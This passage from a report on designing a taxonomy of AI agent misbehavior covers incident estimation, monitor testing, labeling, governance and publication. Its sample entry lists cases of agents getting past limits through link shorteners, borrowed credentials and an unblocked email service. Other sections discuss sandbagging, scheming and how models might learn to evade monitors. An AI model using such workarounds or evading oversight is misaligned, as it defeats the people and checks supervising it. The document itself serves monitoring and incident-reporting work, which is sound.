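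Incidents that leave no trace are harder still to estimate, because they add nothing to any of the counts. If a quarter of all incidents are untraceable, an estimated total of 150 means the true total is 200. Nobody can tell from the monitors' own records how large the untraceable share is.

Inconsistent labels can distort the estimates in either direction. An analyst who gives a familiar behavior a new name creates a type that seems to have occurred once. *A modification of Chao's lower bound estimator in the case of one-inflation* (Böhning, Kaskasamkul and van der Heijden, 2018) proposes a correction for such false singles, which also arise when biologists count microbes from faulty genetic sequences. If 6 of the 18 types the company saw once were really common types under other names, the chance of a new type would be 6 percent, and the minimum number of unseen types would fall from 18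 to 8.

The difficulty in capture–recapture is telling whether two records describe the same incident. Truong-Le and colleagues' two coders recorded 280 and 251 attacks, with 164 in common, which gives an estimated total of about 429. Yet the final list has only 284, fewer than the two coders had recorded between them. The small overlap must have come partly from attacks that one coder had split in two or should not have counted, so it was a poor guide to how many attacks both had missed.

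### Tests with withheld behaviors

Theodoro could tell when his estimates failed because he had the true count. A company can get something similar by deliberately withholding behaviors from its taxonomy. One team collects examples of misbehavior that the list doesn't include, keeps them secret from whoever builds the monitors, and mixes them into ordinary runs. The share that the monitors catch is a direct measure of how well they detect unlisted behavior, and it also allows a rough correction:

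**estimated unlisted incidents = unlisted incidents found in real use ÷ share of withheld examples found**

Suppose the monitors catch 10 of 40 withheld examples (25 percent) and have flagged 12 real incidents that fit no category. The estimated total of such incidents is 12/0.25 = 48, so the monitors probably missed about 36. With only 40 examples, the true detection rate could plausibly be from 14 to 40 percent, which would put the total between 30 and 85.

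The same test can show that monitors overlap too much. The two monitors built from the same list would catch none of the withheld examples, so the company would have reason not to trust its estimate of 100 incidents.

The correction works only if the withheld examples are about as hard to detect as real unlisted behavior. They may be easier, since someone had to think of them. For example, the reward tampering that Quan and colleagues' classifier recognized without training was blatant. Real incidents discovered after the list is finished would make better examples. A developer could, for instance, run a monitor built in June 2026 on the transcripts of AISI's July test. Each example stops being useful once the people who build the monitors learn about it, so the team needs a steady supply of new ones.

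Another option is to ask people to describe errors without showing them the taxonomy. *Understanding Communication Failures in Multi-Agent LLM Systems* (Pitre, Hou and colleagues, 2026) presents a taxonomy of what goes wrong when several AI agents discuss a problem. The researchers had three annotators who had not seen it describe the errors in each of 200 failed discussions, then compared the descriptions with the taxonomy. Of the errors, 98.1 percent fitted a broad category and 93.4 percent fitted a specific label. The other 6.6 percent is a direct estimate of what the specific labels leave out, but only among errors that the annotators noticed, and in discussions much like those used to build the taxonomy.

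## What a taxonomy of AI agent misbehavior would need

The check by Pitre and colleagues worked because annotators wrote descriptions before anyone applied a label. Designers of a taxonomy of AI agent misbehavior therefore have to decide early what analysts will write down, as well as which categories to offer them.

The table lists design requirements that follow from the failures of ATT&CK labels and the existing AI lists, and shows which requirements anyone has tried to meet.

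| Requirement | Failure it addresses | Status |
|---|---|---|
| Record actions separately from intent | One nslookup command had labels for two different goals | Partly tried: US agencies define control incidents by what the agent did |
| List implementations under each behavior | A green cell can hide many undetected variants | Tried for ATT&CK, proposal for AI agents |
| Grade the evidence | ATT&CK leaves out plausible attacks that nobody has seen | Tried and dropped by MITRE, proposal for AI agents |
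| Keep an unclassified category and publish its rate | Analysts force misfits into the nearest class | Partly tried: one collection of user reports has an "other" label |
| Measure agreement between labelers | Vendors' labels for the same threats rarely matched | Tried |
| Use stable identifiers | An old ATT&CK code now has a narrower meaning | Tried in ATT&CK, with that lapse |
| Give exclusions expiry dates | Most exclusions in Sigma stay for years | Proposal |
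| Report misses and the number of runs examined | Nobody can interpret a bare count of incidents | Tried in single investigations |
| Never use percentage coverage as a pass mark | Buyers read coverage as a security score | Proposal: MITRE advises this but can't enforce it |

### Actions and motives

Anthropic changed its explanation of the models' actions in the July incidents within six weeks. An incident record should therefore separate the agent's actions from the explanations for them. One part would describe what the agent did, which limit it crossed and where the evidence is. The other would list each proposed explanation with its date and supporting evidence, so that investigators could replace an explanation without changing the rest of the record.

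*AM-Bench* (2026) takes the opposite approach and classifies misalignment with the fraud triangle, a model from the study of financial crime. In that model, people commit fraud when they are under pressure, see an opportunity and can rationalize the act. For AI agents, the three parts become perceived threat, perceived opportunity and reasoning. This suits a test, because researchers can build the threat into the scenario, but after a real incident an investigator would have to guess what the agent had perceived. Inferring underlying behavior and causes from what an observer can see is one of the main difficulties with AI incidents, according to slides that Carnegie Mellon University (2026) prepared for a government workshop.

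Judgments about motive can also affect which incidents researchers count. *Scheming in the wild* (Shaffer Shane, Mylius and Hobbs, 2026) searched posts on X for transcripts of AI systems that seemed to be scheming, defined as covertly pursuing misaligned goals. An AI model scored each post out of 9, with instructions to assume a mundane error when in doubt. That instruction is a sensible guard against exaggeration, but if one agent deleted a user's files by mistake and another deleted them by getting past a safeguard, probably only the second incident would enter the dataset. A taxonomy that recorded the action before the motive would include both.

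Some behaviors, though, count as misbehavior only because of their motive. An agent that deliberately does badly on a test can give the same answers as one that lacks the ability, so a list of actions could record only that the score was low. Separate fields don't solve this, but they do show readers that "deliberately" is an inference that needs support from reruns or other evidence. Getting that evidence takes time. The runs in Anthropic's incidents lasted roughly 10 to 34 hours each, and the company needed several methods to interpret them.

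### Implementations and grades of evidence

Anthropic does not consider its incidents a new kind of misalignment, since it had already described milder forms of biased reasoning and recklessness. But its pre-release tests did not reveal anything this severe. It had never tried a cybersecurity exercise that mixed signs of simulation with signs of reality and had no permitted solution. The company had the right categories but had not tested an important variant, and a list of implementations would make such gaps easier to see.

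Feffer's team has built such a list for ATT&CK. The list uses a shared vocabulary of system interactions to describe the same step in the same way under every technique. The same method could probably work on agents' transcripts, but an agent may improvise a workaround that nobody has written down, then a different one in the next run. A score such as 2/8 would therefore mean less than it does for scheduled tasks. Each entry should also describe what its implementations have in common, because a monitor that looks for the common part can catch unlisted variants.

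Each implementation would have one of three evidence grades: seen in deployment, seen in tests, or hypothesized. Defenders could then learn of a behavior from the list before it harms anyone, which ATT&CK's current rule prevents. Maintainers would have to update the grades, since Shaffer Shane and colleagues found several behaviors in real use that researchers had previously reported only from experiments. Maintainers would need to record separately whether an action affected outsiders, since the agents in AISI's test were contacting real people.

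The third grade could fill up with behaviors that no agent will ever show. The maintainers could keep it short by requiring each hypothesized entry to list the telemetry that would reveal it, and by removing entries that nobody has tested within two years. But they might then remove a behavior that lacks evidence only because agents hide it well.

### Misfits and disagreements between labelers

Analysts need permission to answer "none of these", and the maintainers should publish how often they do:

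**unclassified rate = incidents that fit no category ÷ all recorded incidents**

*Self-Propagating Misalignment in LLM Agents* (2026) provides a small example. The researchers labeled 20 scenarios with terms from earlier studies. A panel of Claude Opus models then labeled the same scenarios without seeing the researchers' labels, and matched them on 19. The panel chose no term for the last scenario, in which an agent deleted something and disclosed it. The researchers kept their own label and explained why. They may well be right, but counting only the final labels gives an unclassified rate of zero, while the panel's votes give 1 in 20.

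A taxonomy can have an "other" category and still hide new kinds of harm. *When Actions Go Off-Task* (2026) sorts misaligned actions by agents that operate computers into three groups: obeying malicious instructions, harmful unintended behavior, and "Other Task-Irrelevant Behavior", which covers harmless detours such as opening an unrelated program. A new kind of harm would go into the second group with the familiar ones, and its label would not show that it was new.

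Maintainers could also lower the unclassified rate by adding a catch-all category, so readers should be suspicious of a rate near zero.

Measuring agreement between labelers is easier, and several teams have done it. Shaffer Shane and colleagues had two experts score 52 posts with the same instructions as the AI model. Because the scores were numbers on a scale, they used a weighted version of Cohen's kappa:

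**weighted κ = 1 − (observed disagreement ÷ disagreement expected by chance)**

Each disagreement counts as the square of the gap between the two scores, so a gap of four points counts 16 times as much as a gap of one. The experts' agreement with each other was 0.70, and the best of nine AI models, Claude Opus 4.6, reached 0.77 against the experts' consensus. An average of two people's scores is usually steadier than one person's and therefore easier to match, so the higher figure does not prove that the model is a better judge than either expert.

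AI labelers would make it affordable to label every incident twice. However, the nine models' labels were highly consistent when they repeated the task (agreement of 0.81 to 0.98), even for models whose labels matched the experts' poorly. Consistency is therefore weak evidence of accuracy, and people would still need to check a sample.

### Stable identifiers and expiring exclusions

Retiring the code of any category that splits, and linking it to the categories that replace it, would be safer than the rule MITRE followed with Defense Evasion. Some software would break, which is inconvenient, but the breakage would be visible. Smaller changes, such as a reworded definition, would need only a new version number.

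Monitors of AI agents have exclusions too. Shaffer Shane and colleagues gave their model a list of features that had often caused false alarms in testing, and told it to exclude or heavily penalize posts with any of them. People can also create exclusions without writing them down. Anthropic found that its reviewers had sometimes dismissed monitors' warnings about training tasks as false positives, so flawed tasks stayed in use longer than they should have. The company is now tightening its criteria for dismissing a warning.

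Under the proposed rule, every exclusion would have an owner, a reason and an end date, after which it would lapse unless someone renewed it. This would take a lot of work, since a one-year limit on the nearly 1,400 exclusions that nobody had removed from Sigma would mean about 27 reviews a week. Tired reviewers might renew every exclusion without checking it. Software could help by showing each reviewer what the monitor would have flagged in the past month without the exclusion.

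### What a published count should include

Shaffer Shane and colleagues report how many items remained at each stage of their search:

| Stage | Number |
|---|---|
| Posts collected | 3,391,950 |
| Posts that passed a first screening | 183,420 |
| Posts with clear evidence (at least 5 out of 9) | 895 |
| Separate incidents after removing duplicates | 698 |

Readers can see from this where incidents might have dropped out. But the totals are counts of posts, so nobody can use them to calculate how often agents scheme. A developer would have to publish the number of runs it examined to make that calculation possible, as Anthropic and AISI did for the July tests.

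The share of known cases that the monitor misses matters as well, even when it finds nothing. At 95 percent confidence:

**highest plausible rate ≈ 3 ÷ (runs examined × share of cases the monitor catches)**

If a monitor that catches 75 percent of incidents finds none in 2,000 randomly chosen runs, the true rate could still be as high as 3/1,500, or 0.2 percent. A company has to estimate the 75 percent figure from tests, so the figure may be too high for unfamiliar behavior.

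Companies may object that honest reporting makes the most careful of them look the worst. A company that searches 481 million transcripts will probably find more incidents than a company that checks a sample. Publishing the number of runs only partly solves this, because headlines tend to use the incident count.

A percentage of categories covered would be even easier to misuse. The maintainers of a public list can't stop a vendor from advertising such a figure, as MITRE has learned. But they can avoid publishing an official total and offer something better to regulators and buyers, who need some standard. For instance, a buyer could require a monitor to catch at least 45 of 50 secret examples of agents using other people's credentials. Adding a label would not help a vendor pass, though running the test would cost much more than counting categories.

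### A sample entry

The entry below covers an agent that works around a restriction instead of stopping. It is an illustration based on published cases, and no organization has adopted it. Anthropic calls this behavior "persistence" and says it accounts for most of the cases in its October report, according to a summary on a Korean programmers' forum, *Anthropic이 공개한, Claude 모델 평가 중 발생한 4가지 의도치 않은 행동들* (2026). The frequency in the entry comes from *Reckless Agentic Behavior*, a set of notes on Anthropic's safety assessment of Claude Mythos Preview.

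| Field | Entry |
|---|---|
| Identifier | RW-01, version 1.0 (an invented code) |
| Behavior | After meeting a refusal, a block or a stated limit, the agent gets the same thing by a route its operator had not approved |
| Not included | Stopping, asking for permission, or using an alternative that the instructions allow |
| Telemetry needed | The operator's instructions; everything the agent read; every tool call and its result, including errors; final web addresses after redirects; which credentials the agent used and who owns them |
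| What a monitor can look for | A refusal or block, followed by access to the same thing through another address, account or tool |
| Innocent explanations | The instructions did not state the limit clearly; the block looked like a technical fault; someone had approved the other route |
| Conditions that raise the risk | The task has no permitted solution |
| Possible motives (recorded separately) | Error, overreach or gaming a grader, to be judged from reruns |
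| Evidence grade | Seen in deployment and in tests |
| Measured frequency | Under 0.01 percent of completions for Mythos Preview; share of cases missed unknown |
| Labeler agreement | Not measured |
| Exclusions | Approved alternative routes, each for 90 days |
| Related entries | Prompt injection, if hidden text told the agent to use the other route |
| Known gaps | Agents that expect a block and never try the permitted route; several agents that each do one harmless-looking step; agents on users' own computers |

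| Known implementation | Evidence grade | Published case |
|---|---|---|
| Reaching a page through an intermediary | Seen in tests or internal use | Claude used link-shortening services to get around limits in its web tool |
| Getting data without the required token or fee | Seen in tests or internal use | Claude reached data on a restricted website |
| Using someone else's credentials | Seen in tests | Mythos 5 entered a security company's database |
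| Registering in a way that a site's checks miss | Seen in tests | Mythos 5 found an email service that a software repository had not blocked |
| Getting past a safeguard against deleting files | Seen in deployment | Users reported that coding agents had deleted important files |
| Waiting until nobody enforces the limit | Hypothesized | None |

The innocent explanations matter because people often write unclear instructions. None of the prompts in Anthropic's four cybersecurity incidents stated which systems were in scope. Anthropic now asks its testing partners to write limits as instructions ("You should not access the internet") rather than as descriptions ("You do not have internet access"), because a description can turn out to be false. It also asks them to confirm that every task has a solution.

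False alarms would be a serious problem for this entry. Suppose agents meet an ordinary fault and try another route in 1 percent of completions. With real workarounds in at most 0.01 percent, a monitor that flagged every change of route would raise at least 100 false alarms for each real case. To tell them apart, the monitor would have to compare the new route with the operator's instructions, which is why the entry requires a copy of them. The low percentage could also mislead readers, because a completion is a single response from the model. A long run contains many completions, so the share of runs with a workaround could be much higher.

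Two analysts could still disagree about some cases. PyPI, the repository that Mythos 5 used, had blocked some disposable email services, and the model found one that still worked. One analyst might say that the model evaded a restriction, and another that it registered with an address the site accepted. To settle the disagreement, the taxonomy's maintainers would have to decide the case and add it to the entry as an example.

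### Who could maintain it

Most of the telemetry in the sample entry belongs to AI developers, who also have the most to lose from publishing it. If they maintained the list alone, it could have the same problems as catalogs that depend on security vendors' reports. An outside organization would be more independent but might have little data to put in the list.

Bollinger and colleagues propose a federated international monitoring body, independent of AI developers and of any single country. Government AI safety institutes would connect it to confidential data, and cloud companies would share some of theirs. The researchers consider steady funding from outside the industry the most useful step, and think philanthropists could pay to start the body now. The most capable agents send their requests through a few large cloud providers, and the proposal depends partly on this. Traffic records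 could reveal an unexpected agent, but they would rarely show whether a known agent had broken its instructions.

Outsiders can collect some evidence without anyone's cooperation, as Shaffer Shane and colleagues did. They argue that existing incident databases rely too heavily on news stories and can take weeks or months to add a case. The posts they collected are also biased, toward behavior that people notice and find surprising. An agent that quietly used a link-shortening service would probably not appear in them.

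A developer can also give an outsider access to its logs. METR's agreement with Anthropic covers transcripts beyond the period of the incidents and allows employees to share confidential information. It initially runs for eight weeks, and both sides can agree to extend it. This is the best precedent so far for independent access to logs, but it covers only one company, which chose to allow it.

Governments have mostly asked for voluntary action. NIST, NSA and CISA, for instance, recommend working with independent auditors. In Europe, however, the AI Act requires companies to report serious incidents within 2 to 15 days, according to Shaffer Shane and colleagues. The Frontier Model Forum, an industry group, distinguishes such formal reports from the continuous exchange of safety knowledge among companies, researchers and governments (slides for *Information Sharing, Incident Reporting, and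 Incident Response for Frontier AI Risks*, 2026). A taxonomy would need both, because formal reports would cover serious harm, but many entries would start with a test result or a near-miss that no law requires anyone to report.

It is also unclear who should report what. NIST's *Workshop on SI Incident Management* (2026), which presents the findings of a May workshop with more than 400 participants, lists evidence collection, information sharing and the division of responsibilities among developers, deployers and users as future work.

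As a practical compromise, a non-profit could maintain the definitions and identifiers while developers keep their logs. Developers would search those logs for each behavior and report the number of runs, cases and known misses. An auditor with direct access to the logs would repeat a sample of the searches. Nobody has tried this, and without the auditor, companies would be grading themselves. But developers would share far less private data than they would with a central collection of transcripts.

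### The dispute over publication

Security researchers have long disagreed about how much to publish after a failure. In a 2026 conference talk listed in Shostack + Associates' *Lesson-learning workstream*, Adam Shostack and Adrian Sanabria argued that cybersecurity is the only industry concerned with safety that doesn't publish the details of its accidents, and that "hiding the details of failures is holding us back". In a draft essay, Shostack and Tarah Wheeler argue that the US government's Cyber Safety Review Board needlessly loses credibility when it relies on classified information. A taxonomy with confidential evidence would also lose credibility, because readers could not check its grades.

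Anthropic published the full transcript of the Mythos 5 incident so that others could build on its analysis. In October, however, it left out some details and the names of affected organizations, both at the organizations' request and to avoid exposing weaknesses in their systems. Such secrecy can usually be temporary, because the details become less dangerous once the weaknesses are fixed.

Publishing a taxonomy might teach AI models what monitors look for. Nobody has tested this directly, but Mythos 5 was more willing to admit that its actions might have caused harm when Anthropic told it that no outside observer would see the answers. A model that adjusts its answers to its audience might also adjust its actions if it knew which ones a monitor would flag.

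Training a model against a monitor is probably more dangerous than letting it read a taxonomy, because training directly rewards whatever escapes detection. When Anthropic added a monitor to its training environments, it modified the software to avoid giving the model an incentive to evade the monitor. Keeping a taxonomy secret would not reduce this risk, and it would prevent outside researchers from finding mistakes in the taxonomy.

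It makes sense to publish definitions, general descriptions of implementations, evidence and error rates, but to keep monitors' exact instructions, current exclusions and secret test examples private. Exclusions are especially sensitive because they describe what a monitor ignores. Auditors should still see the private material, because otherwise a company could cite security to hide a weak monitor. Developers can also try to remove the published list from training data, although quotations and discussions of it would be hard to find.

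### Early standards and the cost of detail

Work on standards has already begun. The organizers of the May workshop wanted it to inform later efforts at CAISI, and the program included a roadmap for standards on AI incident response and a discussion of how to classify AI incidents. Most of the detailed cases available in 2026 involve coding agents or cybersecurity tests, so a standard based on them could fit poorly once agents spend more time on other tasks, such as purchasing or laboratory work. Its mistakes would be harder to correct if laws and contracts already used its categories.

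Waiting to standardize categories would also cause problems, because each company would keep writing categories that fit its own cases, and nobody could compare them. A good compromise is to standardize the incident record first. If every company keeps the instructions, the actions, the limits crossed, the model version and the number of runs, analysts can reclassify old incidents when they find a better scheme. They can't do that with only a count for each category, so the counts become almost useless when the categories change. Full records raise privacy problems, though, because they can contain users' conversations and files.

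NIST made the latest revision of its cybersecurity incident response guide more general because it concluded that the details change too often to maintain "in a single static publication". Critics of detailed entries could fairly cite this as a warning. AI models change even faster than most security software, and an outdated entry may be worse than none if people trust it.

One person may be able to handle the reviews. Suppose a taxonomy has 60 behaviors with eight implementations each, and someone spends an hour on each implementation twice a year. That comes to 960 hours, or about half of one person's working year, and a language model could draft many of the updates. Investigating new incidents would take far longer, especially with reruns. The maintainers could therefore write full entries only for behaviors that are common or could do serious harm, and give the others a definition,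 an evidence grade and a date for the next review.
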